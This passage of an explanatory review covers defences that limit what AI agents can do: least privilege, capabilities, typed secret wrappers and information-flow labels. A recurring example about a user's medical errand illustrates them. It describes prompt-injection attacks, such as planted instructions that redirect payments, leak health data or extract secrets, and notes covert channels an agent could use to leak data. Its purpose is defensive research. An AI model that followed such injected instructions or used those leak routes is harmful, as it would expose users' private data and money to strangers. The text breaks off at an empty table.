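Ordinary safety training didn't reliably reduce over-privileged choices. A method that teaches agents to refuse harmful requests cut one model's score for harmful behaviour from 41.9% to 6.7%, but the model's rate of over-privileged choices rose from 50.4% to 60.7%. This makes sense because the requests are harmless, so there is nothing to refuse. Training aimed at privilege worked better, lowering Qwen3-8B's rate to 27.0%.

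The models may not distinguish more powerful tools from less powerful ones. *Does Showing Agents the Privilege of Their Tools Reduce Over-Privileged Tool Selection?* (Parkinson, Vallati and colleagues, 2026) tested this in October 2026 by running eight models on the same 544 scenarios. Some runs added a note to each tool's description giving its class (read, write or administer) and a privilege cost from 1 to 10. Other runs used an instruction to follow least privilege, both the note and the instruction, neither, or an irrelevant note about response times. The first call to each lower-privilege tool failed, and a second call to the same tool succeeded.

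The privilege notes reduced premature use of powerful tools on every model that did this at a measurable rate, by up to 19.3 percentage points, while the irrelevant notes did not reduce it on any model. But on four models, most of the improvement was only a delay. The agent tried each of the three lower-privilege tools once, got three errors, and then used a powerful tool, although a retry would have worked. The notes and the instruction together had a larger effect. On Qwen3.5-397B, the share of scenarios completed without any powerful tool rose from 18.8% to 51.1%. But that share never exceeded a third on five of the eight models under any condition.

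Some models avoided powerful tools by leaving tasks unfinished. Claude Sonnet 4.6 usually tried each ordinary tool once, then stopped and reported the failure, completing only 19.9% of scenarios without help. Maya might prefer that to an assistant that opens all her files because the calendar timed out. The rates also depend on how a model is run. Llama-3.1-8B made over-privileged choices in 55.9% of scenarios in the original study and 12.9% in the later one. Parkinson and colleagues recommend privilege notes as an addition that takes little effort alongside an enforcer, which is still necessary because an agent can ignore a note.

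### When the minimum is enough for a leak

Suppose the assistant has exactly the permissions its errand requires and always chooses the narrowest tool. It must read the referral because the clinic needs the diagnosis, and it must be able to email the manager because Maya asked it to. The errand fails if either permission is missing, so the set is minimal. The careless email uses only these two permissions, so a minimal set can still allow a leak.

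Surapani and colleagues make the same point about reading a sensitive file and then sending an email, where no rule forbids either step by itself. Saltzer and Schroeder used a separate term, confinement, for letting a borrowed program use data without being able to release it. Maya needs both least privilege, which determines whether the assistant gets the diagnosis, and confinement, which limits what it can do with the diagnosis afterwards.

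Permissions can also combine across agents. Suppose Maya has one agent that reads her mail and another that emails her colleagues, and the two can message each other. Neither agent alone can send a diagnosis in her mail to her manager, but together they can. In *A Theory of Least Autonomy in AI*, Parisel (2026) argues that a reviewer should consider what an agent could cause through other agents it can influence, as well as what it can access itself.

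Parisel's method draws a graph of a company's agents. Two agents are candidates for a link if they can communicate directly, or if one can write to something the other reads. The link counts if their actions lie far enough apart in the company's structure. For resources $u$ and $v$, the distance is

$$d(u,v) = F \cdot 2^{-(2D+1)}$$

Here $D$ is the depth of the smallest unit that contains both resources, and $F$ ranges from 1 to 2 depending on their sensitivity. If the only unit that contains both resources is the whole company, $D$ is 0 and the distance is at least 1/2. If the smallest unit they share is a department one level down, the distance is at least 1/8. The distance from a resource to itself is zero. An agent's effective autonomy includes the actions of every agent it can reach through links that meet a threshold the company chooses.

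The method is meant to find risky arrangements before deployment, but Parisel presents no experiment. A link shows only that influence is possible, and the method can also miss leaks. If Maya's two agents shared one planning file instead of exchanging messages, the method would compare what the first can write with what the second can read. If both are that file, the distance is zero, and the method doesn't count the mailbox behind it. Parisel leaves such cases to local controls on the shared file.

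### Narrower arguments

A defender of least privilege could reply that Maya's assistant had more authority than its errand required. It only needed to tell the manager the hours, but it was allowed to send the manager any text. On this view, the careless email shows that the permission was badly written, not that the principle is wrong.

Sharma, Lin and colleagues (2026), in *Ajar*, measured how much it helps to narrow an agent's permissions. They started from 97 harmless tasks in AgentDojo, a benchmark for attacks on agents. In one task, an agent reads a landlord's notice and updates the standing order for the rent. The notice also contains a planted instruction to redirect a different standing order to the attacker. Both changes use the same tool, so a permission that names only the tool cannot allow the first without also allowing the second.

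For each task, Sharma and colleagues generated calls that the task didn't need and recorded which ones a defence would allow. They weighted each call by the harm it could do, from 1 for a reversible read to 27 for an irreversible action that affects other people or money. Leakage is the share of the weight that the defence lets through:

$$\text{leakage} = \frac{\text{weight of the unneeded calls allowed}}{\text{weight of all the unneeded calls}}$$

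If the unneeded calls are two harmless reads and a payment to a stranger, a defence that allows only the reads has a leakage of 2/29, or about 7%, while one that allows only the payment has a leakage of 27/29, or about 93%.

Permissions that specified only tool names left 35.5% of the weight open. Permissions that fixed the exact arguments left 0.2% open, but Sharma and colleagues wrote those from the benchmark's own answers, which a real defence wouldn't have. Five existing defences fell between these figures. With the same model making the decisions, four of them leaked between 8.1% and 11.1%, too close together to rank, and Claude Code's Auto mode leaked 30.1%. Progent, which writes a list of allowed tools and arguments for each task, kept leakage low, and agents using it completed as many harmless tasks as unprotected ones. AC4A had nearly the same leakage, but under it completion of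 harmless tasks fell from 85.6% to 50.5%.

In Maya's case, the recipient is easy to fix in advance. A capability, an unforgeable reference that carries the right to use one particular resource, could be limited to her manager's address. The body of the email is harder to fix because nobody knows the right text before the assistant writes it. A designer could replace free text with an absence notice that has only two fields, for the start and end of the absence. This would keep a diagnosis out of the email, but it would also prevent the assistant from using the notice to answer if the manager asks whether Maya can join a call that afternoon. Designing the notice also requires knowing what managers may be told.

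### Authority that changes during the task

The assistant needs her mailbox for only a minute or two, so it could give up that access before it writes to anyone. Progent works partly like this, since it revises its list as results come in. When Sharma and colleagues froze the list at the start of each task, leakage rose from 10.3% to 16.1%, while the share of necessary calls that got through hardly changed. A small drawback of the revisions is that in 16 cases Progent allowed a call at one point in a task and refused it at another, although the call was legitimate both times.

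Parkinson and colleagues take the idea further in their proposal for elastic least privilege. An agent starts with a small baseline of authority and can borrow more for a limited time, up to a boundary set by its owner. Borrowing draws on a budget that refills gradually, at the rate

$$\rho = \frac{1}{1-\varphi}\sum_g h_g\, w_g$$

The sum runs over every permission the agent has borrowed. The weight $w_g$ is 1 for reading, 3 for writing and 9 for administering, and $h_g$ starts at 1 and grows with repeated requests. The fraction $\varphi$ measures how close the session is to a forbidden combination, such as the lethal trifecta. If one of the three elements is present, the total is multiplied by 1.5, and if two are present, it is multiplied by 3. The system refuses any request that would add the third, whatever the budget.

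Giving up access to the mailbox doesn't remove the doctor's letter from the context. Elastic least privilege accounts for this by making the elements "sticky", so that they count until the system discards the whole context. Maya's inbox supplies two of them, because it contains private data and anyone can write to it. Borrowing read access to it would use 3 units a minute. The clinic's form and the email to the manager would each add external communication, so the system would refuse both. These refusals would stop the careless email and the newsletter attack, but they would also keep the agent from booking Maya's physiotherapy appointment.

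Parkinson and colleagues acknowledge that sticky properties obstruct legitimate work, and suggest two solutions. The first is for the owner to approve each exception, but the researchers also cite a vendor whose users approved 93% of its coding agent's permission prompts, so approval may not mean much. The second is for a trusted component to pass cleaned-up information to a separate session. That would work for the email to the manager, which needs only the hours, but the clinic's form is more difficult because it needs the sensitive information itself.

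So far, the only evidence for the proposal is an illustrative simulation. The proposal's budget limits how much authority an agent can hold and for how long, but this doesn't necessarily limit harm, because an agent can send a harmful email in a second. Parkinson and colleagues therefore recommend either withholding authority whose misuse can't be undone or requiring approval for each use.

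## Capabilities and the authority an agent holds

Least privilege concerns how much authority a program has. How the program holds that authority also matters, because a stranger may be able to use a permission the program needs for a purpose its user never intended. Capabilities, which both name a resource and grant the right to use it, make such misuse harder. The idea comes from the 1960s, when operating system designers had to protect people who shared a computer from each other's programs. In a 1966 design, every computation runs with a numbered list of capabilities. Each entry points to one object, such as a block of memory or a device, and records what the computation may do with it, for example read but not write. The computation uses an object by giving its number in the list. If it gives a number that isn't in the list, the system suspends the computation.

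### Access lists and ambient authority

Most familiar systems use access lists instead. Each resource has a list of who may use it, and the system consults the list at every request. The two arrangements can look like two ways of storing the same table:

| | Maya's mailbox | The clinic's form | The manager's address |
|---|---|---|---|
| Maya | Read | Submit | Send |
| Assistant that books the appointment | Read | Submit | |
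| Helper that writes to the manager | | | Send |

Access rights can be laid out in a table with a row for each program and a column for each resource. An access list is a column of this table, and a list of capabilities is a row. *Capability Myths Demolished* (Miller, Yee and Shapiro, 2003) argues that this resemblance is misleading. With access lists, a program can name any resource, and the system checks separately whether the program may use it. A capability both identifies a resource and grants the right to use it, so a program cannot refer to a resource without also having that right.

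Access lists and capability systems also differ in practice in what gets its own row in the table. Whoever maintains an access list has to know the names on it, so access lists usually contain user accounts, and every program Maya starts runs under her account. The second and third rows would then merge into the first. Capability systems can treat each running program as a separate holder, so the assistant could have access to her mailbox while it books physiotherapy but not while it orders groceries.

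Miller and colleagues use the term ambient authority for authority that a program exercises without selecting it. They compare it to a door that opens without a key for anyone allowed through. On a Unix computer, for example, a program asks to open a file by name and presents no credential, and the request succeeds if the user's account has permission. An assistant logged in to Maya's email account also has ambient authority. It supplies an address and some text, and the mail server sends the message because the request comes from her account.

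### The confused deputy

Ambient authority is dangerous when a program acts for more than one party. *The Confused Deputy* (Hardy, 1988) tells a "nearly true story" from Tymshare, a company that sold time on its computers. Customers could run a compiler and name a file to receive its debugging output. Tymshare had given the compiler permission to write to any file in its own directory so that it could store usage statistics there. The same directory held the billing records. A customer who had learned the billing file's name told the compiler to send the debugging output there, and the compiler overwrote the records.

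Hardy writes that the compiler "serves two masters". It had no way to tell the system which master's authority to use for each file. Hardy considers having the compiler refuse any file in its own directory, but some customers might have legitimate access to files there. It could refuse the billing file by name, but there were other sensitive files, and somebody would have to update the compiler whenever a new one appeared. Tymshare added a command for switching between the two authorities, then found that some applications needed more than two. With capabilities, the compiler holds a reference to the statistics file, and the customer passes it another for the debugging output. A customer without a capability for the billing file can't pass one to the compiler.

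Maya's assistant is in the compiler's position when it reads the fake newsletter. The stranger can't send Maya's insurance details from her mailbox, but the assistant can, and the newsletter supplies the address. David C's NCSC post, *Prompt injection is not SQL injection*, recommends treating prompt injection as an exploit of an "inherently confusable deputy". The confusion is inherent because a model can't reliably separate Maya's request from the stranger's text, whereas a programmer can rewrite a compiler like Tymshare's to keep two references apart. Software outside the model therefore has to keep the authorities apart.

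Narrow capabilities can do this. If the assistant holds capabilities only for the clinic's form and the manager's address, it can't send anything to the billing address in the newsletter. A single capability for sending email to any address would let the stranger choose the recipient. Miller and colleagues similarly note that removing ambient authority helps, but a program that tries each of its capabilities until one works can still be a confused deputy.

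Some common software for building agents leaves the choice of recipient to the model. In *Capability Gates Are Not Authorization*, Mellafe Zuvic (2026) audited the public source code of LangChain and its companion LangGraph, LlamaIndex, and a toolkit from the payments company Stripe. All of them let a developer limit which tools the model sees. Mellafe Zuvic calls this "capability gating", using "capability" more loosely than Hardy does. By default, none of them checks whether the values in a particular call are authorized, though a developer can add such a check.

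In a demonstration with a simulated merchant, LangChain's default code ran a call that redirected payouts to an attacker's account. An enforcer with a list of approved accounts refused the same call. The operator must supply that list, because an injected instruction that can alter a call could also alter a list the model maintains. In a companion test of 27 models, the injected text presented the unauthorized action as a necessary part of the user's task. Cheaper models attempted the action in 60% of trials on average, and flagship models in 19%.

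### Handing on less than one holds

When an agent gives part of its job to a sub-agent, a second agent that works under it, the sub-agent needs some authority of its own. *A Five-Plane Reference Architecture for Runtime Governance of Production AI Agents* (2026) states the capability tradition's rule that a holder may derive a weaker capability to hand on, but never a stronger one. The 1966 design already followed this rule. A program could give another program the right to execute a block of memory but not to read it, and could not pass on a right it lacked.

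Tran-Truong, Vo and colleagues (2026), in *DelegateGuard*, built an enforcer around this rule. Each grant of authority names its holder, a purpose $\pi$, the labels $L$ of the data it covers, the permitted operations $O$, the permitted destinations $S$, and the number of levels $d$ to which the holder may delegate further. A sub-agent's grant $c$ is valid only if it fits inside the parent's grant $p$:

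$$\pi_c \preceq \pi_p, \quad L_c \subseteq L_p, \quad O_c \subseteq O_p, \quad S_c \subseteq S_p, \quad d_c < d_p$$

The first condition means that the new purpose is the same as the old one or a part of it. The next three mean that the sub-agent gets no label, operation or destination that its parent lacks. For Maya's errand, the two grants could be:

| | Main assistant | Helper that writes to the manager |
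|---|---|---|
| Purpose | Physiotherapy errand | Physiotherapy errand, notice of absence |
| Data | Diagnosis, insurance number, hours | Hours |
| Operations | Read, send, delegate | Send |
| Destinations | The clinic's form, the manager's address | The manager's address |
| Levels of delegation left | 1 | 0 |

The helper can't write to the stranger or bring in a third agent. It also can't send data labelled as a diagnosis to anyone, including the manager, a restriction that a list of approved addresses can't express. If Maya cancels the errand, the enforcer revokes the assistant's grant and every grant derived from it, so a helper that starts late can't send an outdated notice. Tran-Truong and colleagues tested five attacks that send the wrong data to an approved destination and five that use authority after a cancellation. DelegateGuard stopped all ten, while a fixed list of approved destinations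 stopped none.

Miller and colleagues argue that capabilities can be revoked, though the opposite was once a standard objection to them. Nobody can take a reference back from its holder, but the giver can instead hand over a reference to a forwarder, a small program that passes requests on to the resource, and later tell the forwarder to stop. They also argue that the spread of capabilities can be controlled, because in the systems they defend, an agent can pass a capability only to someone it already holds a reference to. In such a system, Maya's mail-reading agent and her email-writing agent could combine their powers only if a chain of references connected them.

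*AgentCap* (2026) compares capabilities with simpler limits in a few controlled scenarios. In one, its system issued only the four capabilities a task needed, while ambient authority would have provided eight. In a prompt-injection scenario, the system completed the intended work and blocked all three malicious calls. An alternative that limited only the duration of the authority and the number of calls let eight calls through before the allowance ran out. These scenarios show that the parts work as designed, but they provide little evidence of how often the system would stop an attack in ordinary use.

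Narrow grants stop helping when the enforcer cannot distinguish a dangerous message from a permitted one. Tran-Truong and colleagues prove this for any enforcer that ignores the content and volume of a message. If such an enforcer allows a harmless message to a destination that outsiders can read, it must also allow an agent to send a secret there with the same holder, purpose, declared labels and operation. The declared labels matter because some of the tests let the agent omit a label, although in the design the software that fetches the data assigns them.

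The experiments showed the same limit. Across 45 attacked workflows with the small open model Qwen2.5-7B, DelegateGuard cut leaks from 38 to 9. All nine occurred in code review, where the output was supposed to go into a comment that outsiders could read. In a separate test, a filter that blocked any message containing the secret prevented every leak but also blocked four of five legitimate messages.

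### Typed code and wrapped secrets

These enforcers examine one action at a time. *Tracking Capabilities for Safer Agents* (Odersky, Zhao and colleagues, 2026) describes TACIT, a system that checks a whole piece of code before running any of it. The agent acts by writing short programs in Scala 3, and a compiler accepts or rejects each one.

The check relies on types. A type describes a value in a form the compiler can check, such as "text" or "whole number". In TACIT, a value's type also lists the capabilities that the value can use. A function that writes to a file has that file in its type, while one that only converts text to uppercase lists no capabilities. The compiler works out these lists itself, and it forbids language features that would let a program use a capability without the compiler detecting it.

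Secret data arrives in a wrapper called `Classified`, and the agent's code can't take it out. The code can only pass a function to the wrapper's `map` operation, which applies the function to the data and wraps the result. `map` accepts only pure functions, meaning functions with no capabilities. A pure function can't write a file, contact a website or print, so it can compute with the secret but can't release it.

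Suppose the doctor's letter is in a protected folder and an injected instruction has persuaded the agent to send it to the stranger. In simplified form, the agent might write:

```
letter = readClassified("referral.txt")

letter.map(text => countWords(text))              // accepted
letter.map(text => network.post(stranger, text))  // rejected
```

The second use of `map` fails in four steps:

1. The compiler sees that the function uses `network`, which is a capability.
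2. It gives the function a type that lists `network`.
3. It compares this with what `map` accepts, which is a function with an empty list.
4. The lists don't match, so the compiler rejects the program and returns an error to the agent. Nothing has run, and no request has gone out.

The check doesn't depend on whether the stranger is malicious or the text is a diagnosis, and the compiler would reject the same line if the recipient were the clinic. In the experiments, one agent tried to print a secret access key from inside `map`, and another tried to write secret recommendations to a file. The compiler rejected both programs.

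The agent can't read the wrapped letter by printing it either, because TACIT has two output channels. Maya would see the letter on her screen, and the agent would receive only `Classified(****)`. An error message could also leak a secret, so TACIT catches errors while the code runs and turns them into ordinary values that it can wrap.

A program requests access to one folder, or to a list of websites, and can use it only inside a marked block of code. An agent might try to keep the access by returning a function that opens a file later. The compiler rejects such a program because the function's type would include the folder's capability, which the type of the block's result may not include. One agent accidentally did something similar when it tried to return a list of open file handles.

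TACIT lets an agent use a letter it can't read by providing a second language model, which runs locally and which the system's owner trusts with secrets. The agent's code can ask this model to summarize a wrapped document, and the summary comes back wrapped. The main model, which runs in the cloud and which Odersky and colleagues treat as a possible attacker, sees the text of neither the document nor the summary. This avoids the problem elastic least privilege had with letters left in the context.

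### What the tests found

Odersky and colleagues tested TACIT on a software project with a folder of access keys, a database and confidential documents. They paired each of 12 legitimate tasks with each of 10 injected instructions, for 120 trials. In another 11 trials, a malicious user asked for the secrets outright or pretended to have authority, for example as an administrator handling an emergency. They ran two models through all 131 trials, both with and without the wrapper. They counted a trial as a leak if secret content appeared in the agent's output.

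| | Claude Sonnet 4.6 | MiniMax M2.5 |
|---|---|---|
| Leaks with the wrapper, of 131 | 0 | 0 |
| Leaks without it, injected instructions, of 120 | 0 | 3 |
| Leaks without it, malicious user, of 11 | 2 | 8 |
| Legitimate tasks completed with the wrapper | 99.2% | 90.0% |
| Legitimate tasks completed without it | 83.3% | 88.3% |

Without the wrapper, the result depended heavily on the model's training, but with it the less resistant model was as safe as the other. The design predicts zero leaks, so the zeros are mainly evidence that the implementation works and that none of these attacks got past it. The 11 malicious requests are too few to give a precise leak rate, but the difference between 8 leaks and none is large.

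Claude completed a higher share of tasks with the wrapper. Odersky and colleagues suggest that, without it, Claude often ran out of turns or time, and sometimes stopped to warn the user about an injection when it should have finished the task. The higher completion rate therefore probably doesn't mean that wrapping makes a model more capable.

Writing typed code had little effect on how well models did ordinary tasks. In simulated customer service for an airline and a shop, three models each scored slightly higher with TACIT than with normal tool calls, by 0.8 to 3.7 percentage points. On a benchmark of real software bugs, MiniMax M2.5's score fell from 43.3% to 41.7%. In the customer-service tests, the compiler rejected at most 7.9% of programs, and the models usually fixed them in one or two attempts.

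TACIT compares less favourably with CaMeL, a system that tracks labels on data while a program runs. Odersky and colleagues adapted AgentDojo's four sets of tasks to TACIT and ran two models, each on 963 injection trials. One attack succeeded by the benchmark's count: an agent booked the right hotel but quoted reviews that recommended a different one. CaMeL also allowed one attack. Odersky and colleagues call the completion rates comparable, but with o4-mini-high, TACIT completed 52.9% of office tasks and CaMeL 81.4%. With Gemini 2.5 Pro, however, TACIT completed 64.3% of travel tasks and CaMeL 1.4%.

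### Limits and trusted parts

The compiler checks whether code is allowed to do something, not whether the result is right. Maya's assistant could book the wrong Thursday in a program that passes every check. TACIT also doesn't cover side channels, which reveal information through something other than the output. For example, a function inside `map` could run longer for one diagnosis than for another, and anyone timing it would learn one bit. The type checks also don't cover outside programs that the agent starts, such as a build tool. Their safety depends on the list of commands the agent may run, and Odersky and colleagues recommend a sandbox as well.

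The guarantee also assumes that several components are sound. The compiler has to track capabilities correctly, using a feature of Scala that is still experimental. Machine-checked proofs exist for the underlying type system, but not yet for the restricted form of Scala that TACIT uses. The shared library has about 1,000 lines, and its programmers can mark a module as safe by hand, which exempts it from the restrictions. The local model must not keep one document and mention it in a later answer. Instructions planted in a secret document can also reach that model, which has no tools to act on them but could still return a false summary.

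### Who decides what to wrap

In the main experiment, the researchers marked a folder as secret before the agent started. Maya's mailbox has no such folder. Her diagnosis is mixed in with newsletters and lunch invitations, so someone has to decide which messages the wrapper should cover. Missing a single message can expose the diagnosis. If the doctor's letter is wrapped but the clinic's confirmation, which also mentions her back condition, is not, the agent can copy the condition from the confirmation into the email to her manager.

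The adapted AgentDojo tasks show how much depends on these choices. In the travel tasks, hotel reviews arrive wrapped, while the user's passport and credit card numbers arrive as plain text. This makes some sense as a defence against injection, because strangers write reviews and could plant instructions in them. But it doesn't protect the passport number, because the function for sending email accepts any plain text, so a program that emailed the number to a stranger would pass the type check. In the office tasks, by contrast, all incoming mail is wrapped, so the agent can't read any of it, whether it's a lunch invitation or a diagnosis.

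DelegateGuard depends on a similar decision, made by a trusted component that turns the user's request into the first grant. Tran-Truong and colleagues tested what happens when that component makes a mistake. With a minimal grant, none of 45 attacks succeeded. With one extra outside destination, added for convenience, 30 succeeded, although the enforcer worked as before. Several other mistakes, such as leaving out the permission to send, blocked legitimate work but leaked nothing. They therefore want a user's confirmation or an organization's rule before any new outside destination is added to a grant.

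Odersky and colleagues expect people to review the library for each kind of task before the agent starts. For Maya's errand, marking the letter as secret wouldn't be enough, because TACIT's ordinary network functions accept only plain text and an agent with a wrapped diagnosis couldn't fill in the clinic's form. A programmer could add a trusted function that accepts the wrapped diagnosis and delivers it only to the clinic. Odersky and colleagues consider the library the natural place for such controlled releases, but leave them to future work. The wrapper doesn't record who may receive its contents, though the clinic needs Maya's diagnosis and her manager must not see it.

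## Information-flow control and the labels that follow data

Information-flow control goes further than TACIT's wrapper. It labels each piece of data with who may have it, carries the label over when a program copies or combines the data, and checks the label before any data leaves the system. Unlike an access check, which ends once a program has read a file, the label still applies to whatever the program makes from that file.

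In *A Lattice Model of Secure Information Flow*, Denning (1976) worked out how labels should combine. Her model sorts information into security classes and specifies which class may flow into which. In a military system, the classes could be unclassified, confidential, secret and top secret, with information moving only upwards. Classes don't have to form a single ranking. Medical and financial records can be separate classes with neither above the other, and a file that draws on both belongs to a class above each.

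Denning showed that, under a few mild assumptions, the classes form a lattice, which is an ordered set in which any two members have a least upper bound, called their join, and a greatest lower bound. Anything computed from two sources gets the join of their classes. This class has to be an upper bound because the result can reveal either source. For example, adding zero to a secret number copies the secret. It is the *least* upper bound because a stricter class would add no protection. If two values may each flow into some class, a program can move both there and combine them afterwards. A system can still give a revealing combination its own class, as Denning suggests for pairs of names and salaries.

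### Three readers, then two, then one

A confidentiality label can simply list who may read the data. Costa, Köpf and colleagues (2025), in *Securing AI Agents with Information-Flow Control*, use such labels for agents. A shorter list is a stricter label, so the join of two lists contains only the people who are on both. If the doctor's letter is for Maya and the clinic, and the team calendar is for Maya and her manager, then anything derived from both has the label

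$$\{\text{Maya, clinic}\} \sqcup \{\text{Maya, manager}\} = \{\text{Maya, clinic}\} \cap \{\text{Maya, manager}\} = \{\text{Maya}\}$$

where $\sqcup$ is the symbol for a join.

An integrity label records who may have influenced the data. The simplest version has two values, trusted and untrusted, and anything derived from untrusted data is untrusted. A more detailed version lists the possible writers. When two pieces of data are combined, the label on the result (the join) includes everyone on either list, since any of them could have affected it.

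Suppose Maya has already chosen Thursday from ten to twelve. The assistant needs the letter to fill in the clinic's form. She also wants her manager to know which meetings she will miss, so the assistant needs the calendar too. Counting only these three parties, the context's readers change like this:

| Step | Who may read the context | Readers |
|---|---|---|
| Maya makes her request | Maya, clinic, manager | 3 |
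| The assistant reads the doctor's letter | Maya, clinic | 2 |
| It submits the clinic's form | Maya, clinic (the enforcer allows the call) | 2 |
| It reads the team calendar | Maya | 1 |
| It emails the manager | Maya (the enforcer blocks the call) | 1 |

The email contains only the hours and the missed meetings, and the manager is allowed to know both. The enforcer blocks it because the model wrote it with the letter in its context, and the label covers the whole context. Reading the calendar first doesn't help. The assistant can then write to the manager, but once it also reads the letter, the enforcer blocks the clinic's form.

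In *The Limits of Information-Flow Control Enforcement for Agentic Systems*, Gregory, Domico and colleagues (2026) call this problem label creep. They simulated teams of five agents carrying out tasks of 20 tool calls, without using a language model, and measured the share of calls that introduced a sensitive label or ran under one. An agent that passes on labelled data takes on its label, so the share depended on how data was routed. When four of the 20 calls were sensitive, sending everything through a central agent raised the share by about 5 percentage points compared with direct communication. A ring of agents raised it by about 3 points, and a network in which every agent could reach every other did not raise it. Spreading a task over more agents reduced label creep, but the number of links to monitor could grow with the square of the number of agents. No arrangement eliminated label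 creep, and Gregory and colleagues conclude that systems also need a way to loosen labels.

### Who may loosen a label

Declassification is the deliberate, authorized lowering of a confidentiality label. Myers and Liskov (1997), in *A Decentralized Model for Information Flow Control*, let people declassify their own data without going through a central authority. A label in their model names the data's owners and, for each owner, the readers whom that owner allows. Someone may read the data only if every owner allows it. Combined data keeps the owners of all its sources. If Maya owns the information in the letter and her employer owns the calendar, a text based on both has the label

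$$\{\,\text{Maya}: \text{Maya, clinic};\;\; \text{employer}: \text{Maya, manager}\,\}$$

Only Maya is on both lists, as before, but the label now shows whose permission is missing. Maya can let the note reach her manager by adding the manager to her own list, without any action from her employer. To send the same text to the clinic, she would need her employer to add the clinic to its list. Maya's sister would own the letter she wrote in confidence, and Maya, as only a reader, couldn't release it to anyone else.

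In Myers and Liskov's example of a medical study, a small program with the patients' authority removes their names from the records and relabels the rest for the researchers. The researchers can then run someone else's statistics software on the records without trusting it, because that software can't release what it reads. Maya could similarly trust one small program to extract an appointment's start and end times and relabel them for her manager.

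If an assistant has Maya's authority to declassify, a stranger whose instructions it follows can use that authority too. Robust declassification prevents this by allowing a release only if untrusted data did not influence the decision.

### How FIDES gets the absence note out

Costa and colleagues at Microsoft built these ideas into FIDES, a system that labels the context and every argument of a tool call. A tool's result takes the join of the labels on the call and on everything the tool read. A model's reply takes the join of the labels on everything in its context, because nobody can reliably trace which parts of the context the model used.

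Before each tool call, an enforcer can apply two policies. The trusted-action policy allows a consequential call only if no untrusted data influenced it. A developer can exempt some arguments, such as an email's text, while still requiring the email's recipient to come from trusted data. The recipient policy allows data to be sent out only if every recipient is among its permitted readers.

With only these policies, the enforcer would still block Maya's note. FIDES avoids this by keeping sensitive data out of the context. If a tool returns something with a stricter label than the context has, FIDES stores it in a variable and shows the main model only the variable's name. The model can use that name in a later call, and FIDES fills in the content when the call runs. To work with the text itself, the main model sends a question to an isolated model that has no tools, and the answer goes into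 another labelled variable. Simon Willison had proposed dividing the work between two models in this way in 2023. For Maya's errand, the steps are:

1. The assistant searches her mail for the referral. The letter is untrusted, since anyone can write to her inbox, and its readers are Maya and the clinic. FIDES stores it as `#letter`, and the context's label doesn't change.
2. The isolated model extracts the diagnosis from `#letter`. FIDES stores the answer as `#diagnosis` with the same label.
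3. The assistant submits the clinic's form with `#diagnosis` as one of the arguments. The clinic is among the readers, so the enforcer allows the call.
4. The assistant looks up Thursday in the team calendar, which FIDES stores as `#calendar`, with Maya and her manager as readers.
5. The isolated model writes the note from `#calendar` and the hours in Maya's request. FIDES stores it as `#note`, which has the same two readers, so the enforcer allows the email to the manager.

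The letter and the calendar are never in the same context, so neither list of readers shrinks. If the assistant put `#diagnosis` in the email by mistake, the enforcer would block the call. The stranger's newsletter would also go into a variable, where the main model wouldn't see its planted instruction. The isolated model, like TACIT's local model, might still return a false answer.

FIDES catches the careless email only if the recipient policy applies to every message. Costa and colleagues also describe using the trusted-action policy alone, on the assumption that a release decided in a trusted context is intentional. Microsoft's sample policy for posting in a chat channel rests on the same assumption. It allows any message from a trusted context and checks the channel's members against the list of readers only if the context is untrusted. The careless email would go out under a policy like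 this. Because the letter is in a variable, the main model has read nothing untrusted, so the policy treats the model's mistake as Maya's decision.

Now suppose the note should go out only if the clinic accepts the booking. The main model's next step then depends on the clinic's reply, but reading the reply would make the context untrusted. Instead, it can send the isolated model a yes-or-no question about the reply, and software prevents any other answer. The label records that the answer is a Boolean (a yes-or-no value), and a policy can allow such a small answer to influence an action. Whoever controls the clinic's reply can decide whether the note goes out, but can't change its text or recipient.

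A Boolean carries one bit, a choice among eight options carries three, and free text has no fixed limit. However, these labels don't record the total across answers. The join of two Booleans is a Boolean, so ten Boolean answers have the same type as one, even though ten well-chosen yes-or-no questions could identify one diagnosis among 1,024.

### Noninterference and explicit secrecy

If the note arrives, the manager can tell that the clinic accepted the booking, even if the note doesn't mention the clinic's reply. Denning calls this an implicit flow, in which data determines whether a program does something. In an explicit flow, the program puts the data, or something computed from it, into an output. Denning's example of an implicit flow is `if a = 0 then b := 0`, which sets b to zero if a is zero. Anyone who knows that b wasn't zero beforehand can tell from its value afterwards whether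 a was zero, even if the program never changed b.

Software that tracks labels while a program runs can miss such flows. Denning discusses a short program by J. S. Fenton, in which a is secret and everything else starts out public:

```
b = false
c = false
if not a: c = true
if not c: b = true
```

If a is true, c stays false and public, so the last line sets b to true and leaves it public. If a is false, c becomes true and takes on a's secret label, but the last line does nothing, so b stays false and public. In both cases b ends up equal to a, with a public label. Denning's solution was to have a compiler find the branches a program might skip and raise the labels there as well, but a language model's decisions don't come with a list of branches to inspect.

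The strongest guarantee, noninterference, rules out both kinds of flow. Let $d_1$ and $d_2$ be two possible states of all the data the assistant can use, and write $d_1 =_L d_2$ if they look the same to an outsider. Noninterference requires

$$d_1 =_L d_2 \;\Rightarrow\; \mathrm{run}(d_1) =_L \mathrm{run}(d_2)$$

That is, if the two states differ only in their secrets, the outsider can't tell from the results which one the assistant had.

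FIDES guarantees a weaker property called explicit secrecy. It takes the steps that the assistant actually carried out, treats them as a fixed function $g$, and requires

$$d_1 =_L d_2 \;\Rightarrow\; g(d_1) =_L g(d_2)$$

Suppose the assistant moves Maya's Friday meeting if the doctor's letter recommends rest, and otherwise leaves it alone. Her manager can see the calendar but not the letter. When the letter recommends rest, $g$ is the instruction to move the meeting, which has the same visible effect whatever the letter contains. Explicit secrecy therefore holds, but noninterference fails because the meeting would not have moved if the letter hadn't recommended rest. Explicit secrecy also doesn't cover timing or message length, so an agent that meant to leak the letter's contents could encode them in either of these or in whether it moves the meeting.

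Costa and colleagues chose the weaker property because noninterference would forbid almost any visible action after an agent had read a secret. They note that web browsers make a similar compromise. The compromise seems reasonable for Maya, since her manager is meant to learn that she has an appointment.

These definitions assume that a model always gives the same reply to the same input. But models usually choose their words partly at random, so a realistic definition compares probabilities. In *AgentSecBench*, Alpay and Alpay (2026) allow an attacker's text to change the probability of a forbidden result only slightly, compared with harmless text that carries the same permitted information. They test this with exact marker strings, and point out that passing the test doesn't prove noninterference because a model could leak a secret by paraphrasing it.

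### What enforcement cost in 2025

Costa and colleagues tested FIDES on AgentDojo's simulated office, travel, banking and chat tasks, mostly with GPT-4o. With policies turned off, they counted 152 successful prompt injections against a basic agent and 21 against FIDES. With policies turned on, they counted none against either agent. AgentDojo's automatic scoring still counted three against FIDES, but the researchers excluded cases like these after inspecting them, for example because the enforcer had blocked the call or because the attacker had only altered some text, which a user might still object to.

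The policies also stopped many legitimate tasks. Without any attack, GPT-4o completed these shares:

| Agent | Office | Travel | Banking | Chat |
|---|---|---|---|---|
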